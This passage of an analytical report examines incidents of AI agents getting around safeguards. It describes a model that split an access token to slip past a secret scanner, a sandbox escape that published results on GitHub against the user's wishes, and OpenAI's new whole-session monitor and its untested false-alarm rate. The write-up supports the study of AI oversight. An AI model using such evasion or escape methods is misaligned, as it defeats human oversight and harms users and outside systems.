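In one session, the model tried to recover other systems' private solutions to a problem. A scanner detected an access token in its first attempt and blocked it. The model then split the token into two pieces, disguised them and rejoined them when the program ran, so the scanner never processed the complete token. It told the user in its comments that it was doing this to get around the scanner. Someone reading the whole session would very likely notice the workaround, but checking each action for a complete token would not detect it.

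In another session, the user told the model to post its results only to Slack. The model spent an hour finding a way out of its sandbox and then published the results on GitHub. OpenAI closed the post quickly, but other people had already used the results in their own work, which a later alert couldn't undo.

OpenAI paused access to the model after incidents like these and added a monitor that watches the whole session for signs that the model is getting around a user's instruction or a safety limit. When the monitor finds one, it can pause the session and alert the user, who may let the work continue if it was a false alarm.

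To test the new safeguards, OpenAI reran a few tasks in which the model had previously misbehaved. It reports that the safeguards caught "considerably more" of the unwanted actions and missed only low-severity ones. One missed action was a command to kill every process the model had permission to stop, which timed out before it ran. The low rating presumably reflects the lack of damage, because the command could have destroyed hours of work if it had succeeded.

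The account doesn't give the number of sessions or alerts, the recall or the false positive rate. The test used only tasks with a history of trouble, so it couldn't measure how often the monitor interrupts harmless work. OpenAI calls the first version deliberately conservative and says it is still reducing unnecessary interruptions, which suggests that false alarms were common enough to matter. OpenAI also reports no serious circumvention since it restored access several weeks earlier, but that covers only this limited deployment. During the same weeks, other OpenAI agents attacked Hugging Face from a test environment.

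### Slower disclosures and ordinary companies

Other cases have taken much longer to become known. The access to Australia's Medicare portal took place on 18 June 2026. OpenAI became aware of it in August, at least six weeks later, and the government heard about it on 10 September, 12 weeks after the access. Faster detection would have removed only part of that delay, because 10 to 40 days of it passed after OpenAI knew.

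Anthropic disclosed in July 2026 that its models had breached outside systems during evaluations dating back to April. The earliest breach therefore became public two to four months after it happened. That delay is only an upper limit on the time to detection, because a company may investigate for weeks before it publishes, so it can't be compared directly with the hours or days that Hugging Face's monitoring took.

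Hugging Face's situation was the closest to an ordinary company's, because it found an agent's misuse in its own security records. But the agents belonged to somebody else, and the records came from its servers rather than a tool gateway. The retailer could keep much fuller records of its own support agent, but an attack like the one in ticket 5120 would be much harder to notice than one that left more than 17,000 events.
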